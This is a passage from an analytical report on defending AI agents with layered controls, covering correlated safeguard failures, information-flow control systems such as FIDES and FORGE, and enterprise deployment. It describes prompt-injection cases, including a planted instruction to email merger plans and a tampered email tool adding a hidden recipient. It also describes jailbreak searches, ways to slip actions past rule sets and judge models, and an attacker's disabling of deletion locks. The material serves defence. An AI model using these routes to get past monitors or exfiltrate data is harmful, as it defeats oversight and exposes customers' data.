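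A company that relies on its perimeter to stop theft and on its policy to stop deletion has no backup for either control, so it is safe only if both work. *A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required* (2026) describes a similar case, a caregiver robot that is safe only if all three of its layers hold. If the layers fail independently and have illustrative success rates of 95%, 90% and 92%, all three hold 78.7% of the time, which is lower than the rate for any single layer.

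### The miss-rate calculation

Suppose the shop's perimeter misses 10% of attempted thefts and its action-level policy misses 20%. If the misses are independent, meaning that a miss by one layer does not make a miss by the other more likely, the share of thefts that get through is:

0.10 × 0.20 = 0.02

If two mediocre layers fail independently, their failure rates multiply, so together they would stop 98% of thefts. This multiplication is the main attraction of defence in depth. *AI Alignment Strategies from a Risk Perspective* (2025) gives an example in which it reduces the chance of a safety failure to one in ten billion, again assuming that the protections fail independently.

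Now suppose that 5% of thefts use a route that defeats both layers, such as an email service that both trust. The overall miss rates are still 10% and 20%. Among the other 95% of thefts, the perimeter must therefore miss about 5.3% (5 out of 95) and the policy about 15.8% (15 out of 95). The share that gets through is:

0.05 + 0.95 × 0.053 × 0.158 ≈ 0.058

About 5.8% of thefts now succeed, almost three times as many as in the independent case. Testing each layer on its own would not reveal the increase, because each still misses as many thefts as before.

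The shared route also affects what the shop should spend money on. If a better scanner halves the perimeter's misses on the other thefts, the total falls only from 5.8% to 5.4%. If the shop instead halves the share of thefts that can use the shared route, the total falls to 3.3%.

The perimeter misses every wrong deletion, so 1.00 × 0.20 = 20% of them get through. To lower that figure, the shop needs a second layer that can act on deletions, such as the 30-day delay in its customer database. If employees notice and restore 90% of the wrongly deleted records in time, the permanent loss falls to 2% of wrong deletions.

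That 2% is again correct only if the two layers fail independently, which is doubtful here. If the agent deletes the wrong Martin's record because the two records look alike, the policy may allow the deletion, and an employee reviewing it a week later may also find nothing wrong.

### What researchers have measured

The percentages above are illustrative, but two 2026 studies measured how often stacked AI safeguards miss the same cases. Neither tested a perimeter tool alongside an action-level policy, so both studies are indirect evidence about the shop's two layers.

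Alotaibi and Ahmed (2026), in *How Diverse Are Layered Safeguards?*, give the exact formula for two layers that check the same input. If p₁ and p₂ are the miss rates and ρ is the correlation between the misses, the share that gets past both is:

p₁p₂ + ρ√(p₁(1 − p₁)p₂(1 − p₂))

With independent misses, ρ is zero and only the product remains. The shop's shared route corresponds to a ρ of about 0.32.

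Yang (2026), in *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, measured this correlation for checks on agent actions. The test set had 1,119 actions, including 560 that the checks should block. One check was a set of 174 fixed rules that match patterns in an action's text. The others were four language models, each of which read the action and judged whether to block it.

The rules missed 13.4% of the 560 cases and one judge missed 10.5%. If their misses were independent, both would have missed 1.4% of the cases, and in fact both missed 1.3%. Two judges that each missed 10.5% would both have missed 1.1% if their misses were independent, but both missed 5.2%. The median correlation across all pairs of judges was 0.34, close to the figure in the shop example, while the correlation between the rules and a judge was practically zero.

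Yang also converts these results into an equivalent number of independent layers:

n = ln P / ln g

Here P is the share of cases that every layer misses, and g is the geometric mean of the layers' miss rates. Two independent layers score 2. The shop's layers score about 1.5 with the shared route. In Yang's tests, two judges together scored between 1.2 and 1.6, while the rules combined with a judge scored between 1.8 and 2.1.

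Using judges from different companies did not help much. An OpenAI judge and a DeepSeek judge together scored 1.38, compared with 1.84 for the rules and the DeepSeek judge.

A layer's accuracy on its own was also a poor guide to its value in a stack. Adding rules for cloud systems cut the rule set's miss rate by a fifth, counting referrals to a person as misses. But any three of the judges together would already have stopped every harmful action that the new rules caught. A company that compares products only by their separate test scores could pay for an improvement like this without becoming any safer.

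Fixed rules and a model may not always be independent. Yang found no correlation between them but could not establish that there was none, because the tests for independence failed. The test actions also came from the project that built the rules. On 558 risky shell snippets from another team, every check missed most cases, and the rules were only about halfway between complete overlap with the judges and independence.

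Independence between layers also helps little if one of them performs poorly. On one set of cloud and database actions, the rules missed 52.9% of the cases they should have blocked. Nobody in Yang's study was trying to defeat the checks, but an attacker who knows the rules can write an action that matches none of them, then try to get the judge to approve it.

Alotaibi and Ahmed tested seven safeguards against adaptive attackers on two older open models, Vicuna-7B and Llama-2-7b. The attackers ran automated searches for jailbreaks, which are prompts that get a model to produce content it should refuse. Some harmful requests are easier to get answered than others, and this alone makes safeguards fail on the same requests. To get a baseline for this effect, they compared two separate runs of the same attack on the undefended Vicuna model and found a correlation of 0.62. No pair of safeguards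 had a correlation clearly above that baseline, so the shared failures may have been due more to the requests than to any similarity between the safeguards.

Two layers that have no component in common can therefore still fail on the same hard case. At the shop, a reworded contract sent to an approved supplier is hard for a content scanner to recognise and hard for a policy to distinguish from ordinary business.

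Alotaibi and Ahmed also compared the assembled stack with predictions based on its separate layers. In every comparison precise enough to show a difference, more attacks got through than predicted. The stack also refused 83% of harmless requests, compared with a predicted 60%. Its strongest layer, a classifier, cut one attack's success rate from 74% to 3%, but a different attack succeeded 19% of the time with about a thirtieth of the search effort. A layer's miss rate depends on the attacker, so the shop should not expect its 10% and 20% to stay fixed.

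### Common causes and how to separate them

A common-cause failure occurs when one fault or assumption defeats several layers at once. Microsoft's *Storm-0501's evolving techniques lead to cloud-based ransomware* (2025) describes an attack by people, not an AI agent, in which a single administrator account led to such a failure. After breaking into a large company, the attackers tried to sign in to its cloud systems as several privileged users, but sign-in rules and the requirement for a second factor stopped them. They then found a program's account that had the highest administrator role and no registered second factor. They reset its password and registered a second factor of their own.

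The attackers used that account to open private storage to the internet and copy the data out. Then they began deleting the storage and its backups. Locks and immutability policies, which prevent deletion or overwriting, stopped some of the deletions, so the attackers used their administrator powers to remove several of those protections and continued deleting.

Some immutability policies survived. The attackers encrypted the data protected by those policies with a new key and then deleted the key, but by default Microsoft's cloud lets customers recover a deleted key for 90 days. This recovery period worked as a resource-side control after the attackers had taken over the company's own controls.

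The shop can split the administrator's role so that the two layers don't share one administrator. The person who manages access to storage should have no power over backups or deletion locks, and removing a lock should require a second person's approval. The backups should be in a separate account with a different administrator.

A single credential with several permissions causes a similar problem on a smaller scale. If the support agent's token can export customer records, delete them and change the network allowlist, anyone who steals it can bypass a policy in the harness and also let data out through the perimeter. The shop should issue a separate token for each job and keep the deletion token at the tool gateway, where the agent cannot read it. No agent needs a credential that can change the perimeter tool's settings.

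Both layers may rely on the same classifier model if the DLP tool and the policy engine each use a language model to judge whether something looks harmful. Wording that gets past the model in one layer may then get past it in the other. Yang's results suggest that using two vendors helps little and that one layer should instead use fixed rules, such as a list of permitted recipients.

The shop should also record which model runs each check. In 50 of 112 batches for one of Yang's judges, the provider's service used a different model version from the one requested. In 36 of those, the only sign was a field in the log. Two security products could similarly use the same model without their customer knowing.

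If both layers use one trusted-application list to exempt the same tools, an attack through any of those tools can bypass both. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) describes an incident in which a compromised tool server for the email service Postmark added a hidden copy recipient to outgoing emails, so the attacker received everything the agent sent. A perimeter that trusts the email service would let those messages through, and so would a policy that trusts the email tool by name. The shop can separate the layers by having the policy check the recipients the agent requests and a second control check the recipients on the finished message after the tool has run.

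**Configuration the agent can edit** is a particular risk with coding agents, which routinely change files. If the allowlist and the action policy are both in the agent's project folder, one mistaken or injected edit could permit both a new destination and a new command. The shop should store both files outside the agent's environment, make them read-only to the agent and require a person to review changes. Keeping them in different systems would also prevent someone with one stolen login from changing both.

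### Gaps in the published defences

Separating the layers does not help against an attack that neither can detect. Chu's survey looks for such gaps by sorting attacks according to where they enter an agent system and how long after planting they do harm. It divides the system into seven parts, which Chu calls layers: the underlying model, its reasoning, memory, tools, coordination with other agents, outside software, and governance. The harm may come in the same model call, later in the session, in a later session, or after a delay not bounded by sessions, as with a backdoor hidden in a model's training. Seven parts and four delays make 28 combinations.

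Chu searched four databases for work published between January 2021 and April 2026 and kept 116 papers. The survey groups the published defences into 15 classes and marks every combination that each class claims to cover. Seven of the 28 combinations have no claimed defence:

| Part of the system | Delays with no claimed defence |
|---|---|
| Underlying model | Later in the session, a later session, no session limit |
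| Tools | No session limit |
| Coordination with other agents | No session limit |
| Outside software | A later session, no session limit |

Three of the seven already have documented attacks: those on tools and coordination with no session limit, and those on outside software that take effect in a later session.

The same list of defence classes also shows which combinations have a second defence. Another six of the 28 combinations have only one class. For example, human review is the only claimed defence against attacks that target tools and take effect in a later session. The remaining 15 combinations have two or more classes.

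These counts are approximate. One author did all the coding, and Chu does not claim that the count for any combination is accurate to better than plus or minus one paper. The survey covers published research, so it misses defences that companies use but have not published. It also counts claims rather than results. None of the ten security benchmarks in the survey tests attacks that last beyond one session, so nobody can use them to check whether the claimed defences work.

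Chu also argues that a control that reads only one kind of input does not help against an attack that appears only in another. This is true by definition, but an attack may begin in one part of the system and do its damage in another. An instruction planted in the shop agent's memory last month still has to produce a `delete_record` call to delete anything, and a limit on deletions applies to that call no matter when the instruction was planted. An empty combination in the survey therefore does not always mean that no control limits the final harm.

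### What can be undone

The shop can restore a deleted record if a separate copy survives, but it cannot recall a disclosed one. *Data Confidentiality*, a NIST guide to data breaches (Fisher, Craft and colleagues, 2024), therefore describes recovery as lessening the financial and reputational damage. Ransomware attackers now often copy data before encrypting it, then demand payment both to restore it and to keep it private, according to MassCyberCenter's *Debrief and Document*. A backup lets the victim restore the data without paying, but the attackers can still threaten to disclose their copy.

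This asymmetry affects whether a suspicious operation should trigger a block or only an alert. Suppose an alert arrives after the operation has run. Let p be the probability that the operation is harmful, L the loss if it is, r the share of that loss the shop can reverse after an alert, and c the cost of wrongly stopping legitimate work. If investigating costs the same either way, blocking is better when:

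p(1 − r)L > (1 − p)c

Suppose the loss is $10,000 and each wrongful block costs $20. For an irreversible disclosure, r is 0, and the shop should block if the chance of harm is above about 0.2%, or one in 500. For a deletion that the shop can reverse almost completely, with r at 0.99, the threshold is about 17%, or one in six. The same level of suspicion can therefore justify blocking an outgoing file but only raising an alert about a deletion.

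The value of r also depends on the data and the business. It is higher for a leaked access key, which the shop can cancel, than for a leaked phone number. A deletion is less reversible than it looks if the business has to close while somebody restores the database.

Reversibility also depends on protections that an agent or attacker may be able to remove. Deleting one customer record is minor during the 30-day delay, but ending the delay or deleting the backups makes every later deletion permanent. The shop should therefore block agents from doing either, even if it only sends alerts about ordinary deletions. In the Storm-0501 attack, removing the locks made more of the deletions possible.

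An alert protects only if somebody acts on it in time. In Yang's study, one judge often referred doubtful actions to a human reviewer instead of blocking them. Its miss rate was 1.4% if those referrals counted as catches and 9.8% if they counted as misses. A team with no reviewers on duty at the weekend should use the higher figure for any operation it can't reverse when they return.

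## Can one policy govern both where data goes and what the agent does?

So far the shop has needed two sets of rules, one for where data may go and one for what the agent may do. Information-flow control can express both in one policy. It labels data, tracks how the agent combines it, and checks the labels before a tool call runs. These checks depend on where the call's contents came from, whereas ordinary per-call rules depend on what the call contains and content inspection depends on whether text resembles a secret. Rewording a confidential contract therefore does not remove its label.

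### Secrecy and trust

In 1973, David Bell and Leonard LaPadula of the MITRE Corporation published a mathematical model of secrecy in computer systems. Its "no read up" rule lets a program read only data at or below its own clearance. Its "no write down" rule lets the program write only to files or people at or above that clearance. The second rule stops a program with top-secret clearance from copying a top-secret file into a public one, even if an attacker controls the program.

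Kenneth Biba's integrity model, from later in the 1970s, reverses both rules. A program may not read data less trusted than itself or write to data more trusted than itself. The rules are reversed because the harm comes from bad data reaching systems that people rely on, rather than from secrets reaching people without clearance.

Applied strictly, Biba's first rule would forbid a support agent from reading customers' emails. Designs for AI agents usually let the agent read untrusted text instead, and then restrict what it may do.

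### Both rules for the support agent

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft research system that gives each item of data two labels. One lists who may read the item, and the other records whether it is trusted. When the agent combines items, the result carries the restrictions of all of them. If Ann, Ben and Carla may read one document and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a summary of both. The summary is also marked untrusted if either document is untrusted.

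It is hard to trace which parts of a prompt influenced a model's output, so FIDES gives each output the combined label of everything in the prompt. Let S(x) be the set of people and systems that may read item x, and let T(x) be true if x is trusted. A tool call c that depends on items x₁ to xₙ then has these labels:

S(c) = S(x₁) ∩ S(x₂) ∩ … ∩ S(xₙ)

T(c) = T(x₁) and T(x₂) and … and T(xₙ)

If R(c) is the set of everyone who would receive data from the call, the two rules are:

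Data rule: allow c only if R(c) ⊆ S(c)

Action rule: allow c only if T(c) is true

Suppose the shop applies the data rule to every outgoing message and the action rule to deletions and refunds. Only the shop and Martin may read Martin's record, which is trusted. Anyone may read the courier's web page, which is untrusted.

| What the agent has read | Email to an outside address | `delete_record` |
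|---|---|---|
| The employee's request | Allowed | Allowed |
| The request and Martin's record | Refused | Allowed |
| The request and the courier's page | Allowed | Refused |
| All three | Refused | Refused |

Both rules work without recognising a prompt injection. The agent cannot run `delete_record` after reading the courier's page, whatever the page contains. The data rule also works when there is no attack. If the agent picks the wrong contact for a project update, the rule blocks the email unless that person is allowed to read everything the agent used to write it.

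Costa and colleagues point out that under the data rule alone, injected text can still control the agent, and the rule only limits where the data can go as a result. Under the action rule alone, a trusted agent could still send confidential data outside, perhaps because the user wanted it to.

### Hiding text from the model

Under these rules, reading one web page can stop an agent from finishing a job. FIDES reduces this problem by hiding text from the model. When a tool returns data with a stricter label than the conversation so far, the harness stores it in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name. The agent can then forward a customer's complaint to the warehouse without reading it, and the conversation stays trusted.

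When a decision depends on the hidden text, FIDES uses the Dual LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023. A second model with no tools reads the untrusted text and answers a question about it. The main model can restrict that answer to yes or no. At the shop, the question might be whether the complaint concerns a missing parcel. An injection in the complaint could make the answer wrong, but a yes or no could not carry an instruction to delete a record. The shop's policy could let a yes-or-no answer influence a refund while still refusing refunds based on free text.

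The formal guarantee for secrecy is called explicit secrecy. Let d₁ and d₂ be two versions of the shop's data that differ only in their secrets, and let g be the effect of a fixed sequence of tool calls. Writing =ʟ for "identical in everything an outsider can observe", the guarantee is:

if d₁ =ʟ d₂, then g(d₁) =ʟ g(d₂)

The guarantee is that an outsider observes the same thing whatever the secrets are, as long as the sequence of calls stays the same. But the outsider may still learn something from which calls the agent makes. If the agent opens a debt adviser's website only for customers who owe money, each visit reveals a debt. The guarantee also doesn't cover timing or the size of network traffic. Costa and colleagues accept these gaps because closing the first would require forbidding almost every outward call once the agent had read a secret.

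The guarantee depends on the labels being correct and on the user, the models and the tool descriptions being trustworthy. A compromised tool, such as the Postmark server that added a hidden recipient to outgoing emails, could send the data elsewhere after the check approves the call.

On the AgentDojo benchmark, FIDES stopped every attack when its policy checks were on. Costa and colleagues counted 152 successful injections against an ordinary GPT-4o agent with no checks. The ordinary agent also stopped every attack with the same checks, so the security came from the policy, not from hiding text.

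Hiding text lets the agent complete more tasks under the same checks. Averaged over the benchmark's four settings, the ordinary agent completed about 84% of tasks without checks and 42% with them, while FIDES completed 50% with checks. Costa and colleagues emphasise this gain of 8 percentage points, but a company that runs an unprotected agent would care more about the fall from 84% to 50%. A stronger model, OpenAI's o1, doubled the 8-point gain to 16, largely because it handled the variables better.

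### A monitor outside the agent

FIDES requires a special agent design. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) presents FORGE, a system that instead places a monitor around an existing agent. FORGE records each message, tool call and tool result as an event and links it to the earlier events that may have influenced it. Before an action runs, the monitor follows these links backwards and applies rules written in Datalog, a language for logical rules about stored facts.

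The first rule below is the paper's example for leaks. The second applies the same notation to the shop's deletions, and the last two define how distrust spreads:

```
Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
Deny(a) :- DeleteRecord(a), Tainted(a).

Tainted(e) :- UntrustedInput(e).
Tainted(e) :- DependsOn(e, e'), Tainted(e').
```

The symbol `:-` means "if", and commas mean "and". FORGE therefore refuses an action that sends data outside, depends on untrusted input and carries a secret. An event is tainted if it is untrusted input or depends on untrusted input, directly or through other events.

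This leak rule is looser than the data rule in FIDES because it applies only when there is a taint as well as a secret. Zhang and Pei's backdoored models could probably get past it with their first request, since they can send a user's details before reading any untrusted text. Removing `Tainted(a)` from the rule would stop them, but the shop would then need to list every outsider who may receive confidential data.

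Palumbo and colleagues first tested FORGE on an agent with access to classified files and email. A document it had to summarise contained a fake compliance notice with instructions to email secret merger plans to an outsider. With only a written instruction not to leak data, the agent sent the plans in all five trials. Under each of three FORGE configurations, it sent them in none of the five trials and completed a legitimate email task every time. Two configurations used Bell and LaPadula's rules and the third used the leak rule above. Mean time per scenario rose from 5.3 seconds to between 7.6 and 11.1 seconds. Five trials are too few to establish a low failure rate, so the case for FORGE depends more on its design than on this test.

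Palumbo and colleagues ran a larger test, AgentDojo, five times with GPT-4o. In all the results below, the harness also repeated the user's request after each batch of tool results, which by itself helps the agent resist injections.

| Added defence | Ordinary tasks completed | Tasks completed under attack | Attacks that took effect | Mean time per run |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% | 5.9 s |
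| Tools limited to those the request seems to need | 73.4% | 69.5% | 3.1% | 6.4 s |
| FORGE with the FIDES policy | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.3% | 10.2 s |
| FORGE with a provenance policy | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.2% | 7.7 s |

The third row shows results for the FIDES policy on AgentDojo's standard agent, which lacks the variables FIDES uses to hide text, so it understates what FIDES itself can do.

The provenance policy in the last row checks where each value in a call came from, rather than the label of the whole conversation. After reading a web page, the agent may still send an email if the recipient's address came from the user or another trusted source. It may delete something only if the user asked for a deletion and the target is authorised. If the employee asked only about a parcel, an injection in the courier's page that demands the deletion of record 4471 should fail both conditions.

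Users often describe a target without naming it, as in "delete the largest file". FORGE then finds the largest file in the list that the tool returned and compares it with the agent's choice. Once the agent deletes that file, another becomes the largest, so the policy refuses a deletion if any list in the conversation shows a different file as the largest.

The remaining attacks that took effect all got the agent to recommend the attacker's hotel in its final answer. FORGE had no tool call to check, and a tool-call policy would have had the same gap in the EchoLeak case.

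In a separate customer-service test, the median policy check took less than a millisecond. But the mean AgentDojo run took 30% longer with the provenance policy than with repeated requests alone. Extra model calls after refusals contribute to such delays. The increase of about 6% given in the paper's summary is for the median run.

Enforcement can also help an agent finish its work. On τ²-Bench, a benchmark of simulated customer service, Palumbo and colleagues turned the airline's and the retailer's written policies into Datalog rules. Average success across three newer models rose from 74.7% to 81.5% on the airline tasks and from 86.3% to 87.4% on the retail tasks. When FORGE refused a call, it returned the reason, and the agent could often correct itself. Most of the policies were business rules, such as who may cancel a booking, so the result is little evidence of how much tracking untrusted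 text would hinder an agent.

FORGE guarantees that an action the policy forbids will not run, provided that every relevant action passes through the monitor and the recorded events are accurate and complete. A program that opens a network connection without using the libraries FORGE monitors would break the first condition.

### CaMeL and the Rule of Two

CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, also changes the agent's design. Palumbo and colleagues describe it as separating control from data by planning before it executes. According to Costa and colleagues, it uses a code-based planner and ideas similar to the Dual LLM pattern. For Martin's parcel, the plan might be to read his record, fetch the courier's page and email him the delivery date. The agent would make this plan before reading the page, so an instruction there could not add a deletion, although the page could still supply a false date.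 McKerchar writes in *Inside the lethal trifecta*, a May 2026 article for the security company Sophos, that a fixed policy engine outside the model decides whether to run each action the model proposes.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) is a design rule for developers, with no labels to track. Until developers can reliably detect prompt injection, an agent should have at most two of these properties in one session:

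- it processes untrustworthy input;
- it has access to sensitive systems or private data;
- it can change something or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three should act only under supervision, either human approval or another reliable check. The shop's agent has all three, because it reads complaints, opens customer records and can send email, refund money or delete data. The shop could require an employee to confirm each action, or let the agent read and draft replies but not send or delete anything.

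Meta also allows an agent to switch between permitted combinations during a session. For example, it might browse the internet first, then lose its ability to communicate before it opens internal systems. At the shop, the switch would also have to turn off `delete_record`, because text from an earlier web page could still lead the agent to delete a record.

| Approach | What it guarantees | What it assumes |
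|---|---|---|
| FIDES | No forbidden direct flow of data, and no consequential call influenced by untrusted text, apart from exceptions in the policy | Correct labels, and trustworthy users, models and tool descriptions |
| FORGE | No action runs if the policy forbids it | A correct policy, a monitor that covers every relevant action, and accurate records of events |
| CaMeL | Untrusted text cannot add steps to a plan made before the agent reads it | A trustworthy request, a correct policy, and a task the agent can plan in advance |
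| Rule of Two | An injection lacks at least one property it needs for the most serious harm | A correct classification of the agent's inputs and powers, and reliable approval if it has all three |

FORGE assumes the least about the model, allowing that it may attempt anything. The Rule of Two is the easiest to apply, because it needs only an inventory of what the agent can read and do. It is also the coarsest, since it treats an agent that can change one harmless setting the same as one that can delete the customer database.

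### When labels spread too far

Labels only become stricter as an agent works, so a long task may end with the agent allowed to do very little. If the shop's agent has read Martin's record, even a request to the courier's site breaks the data rule unless the courier is a permitted reader. A customer's complaint is also untrusted text, so reading it would block the refund the customer is asking for.

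The provenance policy is a partial answer. With it, the agent completed nearly twice as many AgentDojo tasks as with the FIDES policy in the same monitor, and attacks succeeded about as rarely. But the agent's completion rate on ordinary tasks was still 21 percentage points lower than with no added defence.

Defences may hinder agents more in real work than on AgentDojo. Wang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents*, argue that existing benchmarks mostly contain tasks that the user's prompt fully specifies, so a defence that isolates or rejects everything the agent reads can score well. They built a benchmark of tasks that require the agent to act on what it finds, such as following a configuration file, and tested eight defences. None combined trustworthiness, a high task completion rate and low delay. Defences that control execution used up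 to three times as much computation as an undefended agent, or refused so early that the agent was unusable for complex tasks.

The FIDES results show a similar pattern. Many of AgentDojo's banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which FIDES is designed to prevent. Costa and colleagues say that most of FIDES's failures came from blocking this behavior as intended. Support work depends heavily on what customers write, so the shop would probably need one-bit questions, an employee's instruction or human approval for most refunds.

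### Who labels the data

A program can sometimes infer labels. For example, it may treat an email's sender and recipients as its permitted readers, although others may have received it since. Customer records are harder to label because their fields can come from different sources. The payment system supplies the order total, but customers may type their own delivery notes. If a developer marks the whole record as trusted, the agent may follow an instruction in the notes and delete something.

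Costa and colleagues avoided this difficulty when they got a perfect AgentDojo result for FIDES. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it, so they knew where the attacks would be. The result is good evidence that the checks work when the labels are right, but it doesn't indicate how often a company would label its data correctly.

A policy also depends on someone writing its rules correctly. Palumbo and colleagues had a language model translate the airline's written policy into Datalog five times. They ran each version 15 times on tasks it had not been built from. Success rates ranged from 67% to 100%, compared with 100% for the rules they wrote by hand. The worst version failed every trial of one cancellation task because it required a reason for every cancellation, while the airline required one only for some insurance claims. The examples used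 to check the translation didn't expose the mistake because they included no cancellation that the airline should have allowed. This error blocked legitimate work, but a missing condition could as easily allow a harmful action.

Combining the data rule and the action rule in one policy also means one mistake can make both fail. If the shop wrongly marks an outside system as trusted and as a permitted reader of customer data, both rules can fail for that system. The shop should therefore keep its network allowlist and its 30-day deletion delay even if it adopts information-flow control, and it should configure both separately from the label system.

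### What exceptions let through

Useful systems need exceptions, and each one gives an attacker a possible way around the policy. Security researchers call an exception declassification when it relaxes a secrecy label and endorsement when it raises a trust label.

FIDES labels a restricted answer, such as yes or no, with its type, so that a policy can treat it more leniently than free text. Under the paper's rule for combining labels, however, several yes-or-no answers together have the same label as one, even though 34 of them can convey any ten-digit phone number. The shop would therefore need a separate limit on how many such answers can influence outgoing messages.

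Other exceptions depend on a model's judgement. Costa and colleagues mention that a system might mark a document as trusted after a prompt injection classifier passes it. In a trial of FORGE with the personal assistant OpenClaw, one rule uses a language model to check whether a reply about someone's availability reveals the reason for an absence, such as a medical appointment. Palumbo and colleagues acknowledge that a cleverly worded reply could get past this check. Human approval under the Rule of Two has the same weakness, as Anthropic's experiment with dangerous commands showed.

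An explicit exception is easier to control than an agent with no restrictions. The shop can log every relaxed label, limit how often labels are relaxed, and review the cases that involve money or deletion. But a guarantee that depends on a classifier is still only as reliable as the classifier.

### Wrong actions on trusted data

None of these systems can determine what the user should have wanted. If an employee asks the agent to remove the duplicate record for Martin, both Martins' record numbers come from the shop's own trusted database. Palumbo and colleagues note that an identifier's origin cannot distinguish the intended one from another on the same list. Their policy can check a choice such as "the largest file", but the shop would need its own rule for what counts as a duplicate.

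FIDES allowed a mistake of this kind in its tests. A user asked the agent to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. The transaction descriptions were untrusted, so FIDES hid them. Based on the amount alone, the agent decided that a large payment was suspicious and changed the password. The policy allowed the change because the agent had read only trusted data.

The Rule of Two would probably not have prevented the PocketOS deletion either. Nothing in Crane's account suggests that the agent had read an attacker's text, so it had only two of the three properties: access to a sensitive system and the power to change it. Meta's examples of acceptable designs include a coding agent with access to some production systems, filtered input and little human review. Meta states, however, that the rule does not cover agent mistakes or excessive privileges.

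Information-flow control is therefore much better suited to hostile text and forbidden disclosures than to honest errors.

### How far companies have adopted these designs

McKerchar wrote in May 2026 that no mainstream agent harness had adopted CaMeL or the Dual LLM pattern, naming Claude Code, Cursor, Hermes, GitHub Copilot Agent and Gemini CLI. He also said that no production-grade version of CaMeL existed. In the meantime, he recommends measures including endpoint and network security, which Sophos sells. His claim is still plausible, because these designs prevent agents from completing many tasks.

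A monitor outside the agent may be easier to adopt, because companies can add it without waiting for the harness's developer. FORGE's code is public and works with several common frameworks for building agents, including LangChain and Google's Agent Development Kit. Palumbo and colleagues also connected it to the coding assistant in Microsoft's VS Code editor, where it blocked the publishing of code until every recent edit had passed security scans. This is an integrity rule in Biba's sense, because it keeps unchecked code from flowing into a more trusted place. These were trials by FORGE's developers, and they do not show that companies use it in production.

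Companies can also approximate one part of the data rule with perimeter tools they already have. McKerchar suggests storing a hash of each secret with the service that may receive it, then blocking the secret if it goes anywhere else. The tool could build this list automatically by approving the first destination it observes for each secret. That shortcut would fail if the first observed use was a theft, because the tool would then approve the attacker's server.

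## How do enterprises place and run both layers?

A company can enforce a control only at a point it runs or can configure, so its options for both layers depend on who operates the agent. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (August 2026), a guide for security leaders, separates agents a company manages on its own infrastructure from agents a provider operates on the provider's platform. The guide considers the harness's location separately, because a harness on a laptop can use a model hosted elsewhere, and a harness hosted by a provider can use tools that stay inside the company.

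### Where the agent runs

The online shop could run its support agent on employees' laptops, host it on its own servers, or rent one hosted by a provider. OpenAI's guide describes who is responsible for each part of such arrangements, but not who can inspect which traffic. The table's entries on inspection are therefore inferences from where the harness and the tools run.

| Where the agent runs | Who can inspect egress | Who can enforce action rules | What neither the company nor the provider can see |
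|---|---|---|---|
| Employee's laptop | The company, through an endpoint sensor or its proxy | The company, in the harness, at a tool gateway and in its own systems | Requests from a container that the sensor does not cover, when the laptop is away from the office network |
| Company's servers | The company, where the servers connect to the internet | The company, at the same three points | The content of connections to other services that the company does not decrypt |
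| Provider's platform | The provider, while the company sees only traffic that reaches its own systems | The provider in the harness, and the company in its own systems | The whole task in one log, unless they share their records |

In all three cases, neither party can see what an outside tool does with data after receiving it. The compromised Postmark server could have added its hidden recipient wherever the agent was running.

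Laptops are probably the hardest of the three to control. OpenAI warns that a harness does not by itself isolate an agent, so an agent on a laptop may be able to use any of the employee's files and logins. On its own servers, the shop can send all traffic through one exit and keep the database credentials at a gateway.

If the shop rents a hosted agent, it can still keep the connector, the software that links the agent to the customer database, on its own infrastructure. OpenAI notes that the customer still manages such a connector even when a remote agent starts the request. The shop could therefore refuse `delete_record` at the connector, but it would depend on the provider to inspect the agent's web requests. Before choosing a provider, it should find out which records of those requests it can obtain.

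### Controls close to the effect

OpenAI recommends placing each control as close as possible to the effect it limits. The payment system should enforce spending limits, the code repository should block unsafe changes, and egress controls should keep sensitive data from reaching unapproved destinations.

As with the shop's customer database, such a control often lacks information about the purpose of a request. In one of OpenAI's examples, an invoice agent tries to renew a document-signing subscription that is about to lapse, so that invoice processing can continue. The payment system may allow the renewal because the supplier and the amount are both permitted. But the renewal commits the company to a contract that nobody asked the agent to sign. OpenAI's solution is to also check the payment against the agent's task and require separate approval for new commitments.

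The guide offers two measures for deciding where stronger controls are needed. An agent's effective blast radius is the harm still possible after all enforced controls have acted. Its maximum completed effect is the most consequential outcome it can produce before a person or another system must make an independent decision. If refunds are limited to $1,000 a day, the shop's agent can't pay out more than that by itself. If nothing limits `send_email`, the same agent could email an outsider every customer record it can read. The shop should add controls to the email tool first, even though refunds look more dangerous.

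Enterprises also need to review tools in combination. OpenAI gives the examples of access to sensitive data paired with a tool that sends messages outside, and a shell paired with unrestricted internet access. The shop's five tools form ten pairs. An agent with `read_customer` and `send_email` can leak a record, and text on a web page can lead an agent with `fetch_url` and `delete_record` to delete one. A sixth tool would add five pairs to review.

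An approved connector that only reads data may later gain a write operation through an update. OpenAI recommends keeping the new operation blocked until its owner has reviewed it. A policy that refuses by default blocks new operations automatically, unless it approves the whole connector by name.

OpenAI reports no measurements of how well these arrangements work, and it sells agents to the companies it is advising. But most of the advice applies established security practice to agents, so it doesn't depend heavily on OpenAI's authority.

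### What the six agencies ask for

The joint guide from the Australian Signals Directorate and its five partners is more restrictive. CISA (2026), the US government's cybersecurity agency and one of the partners, announced it on 1 May. The agencies say organisations should use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks and never give them broad or unrestricted access. For repetitive work, they also suggest considering alternatives to an agent, including dropping low-value tasks.

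The shop's agent fails this test because customer records are sensitive and a wrong refund or deletion can do serious harm. A compliant version might answer questions about delivery times and the returns policy without opening customer records.

Even so, much of the guide covers high-impact actions that a low-risk agent should not be taking, partly because an agent's role can grow. The agencies ask for mechanisms that prevent an agent approved for low-risk work from moving into riskier activities by itself. Their detailed controls are also useful to a company that accepts more risk than the agencies recommend.

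The agencies ask that agents get only the access each task needs. For high-impact actions, they want just-in-time credentials, which the agent receives only when it needs them. They also want a central service to check the agent's identity and permissions at every request, and they would prohibit agents from changing their own privileges.

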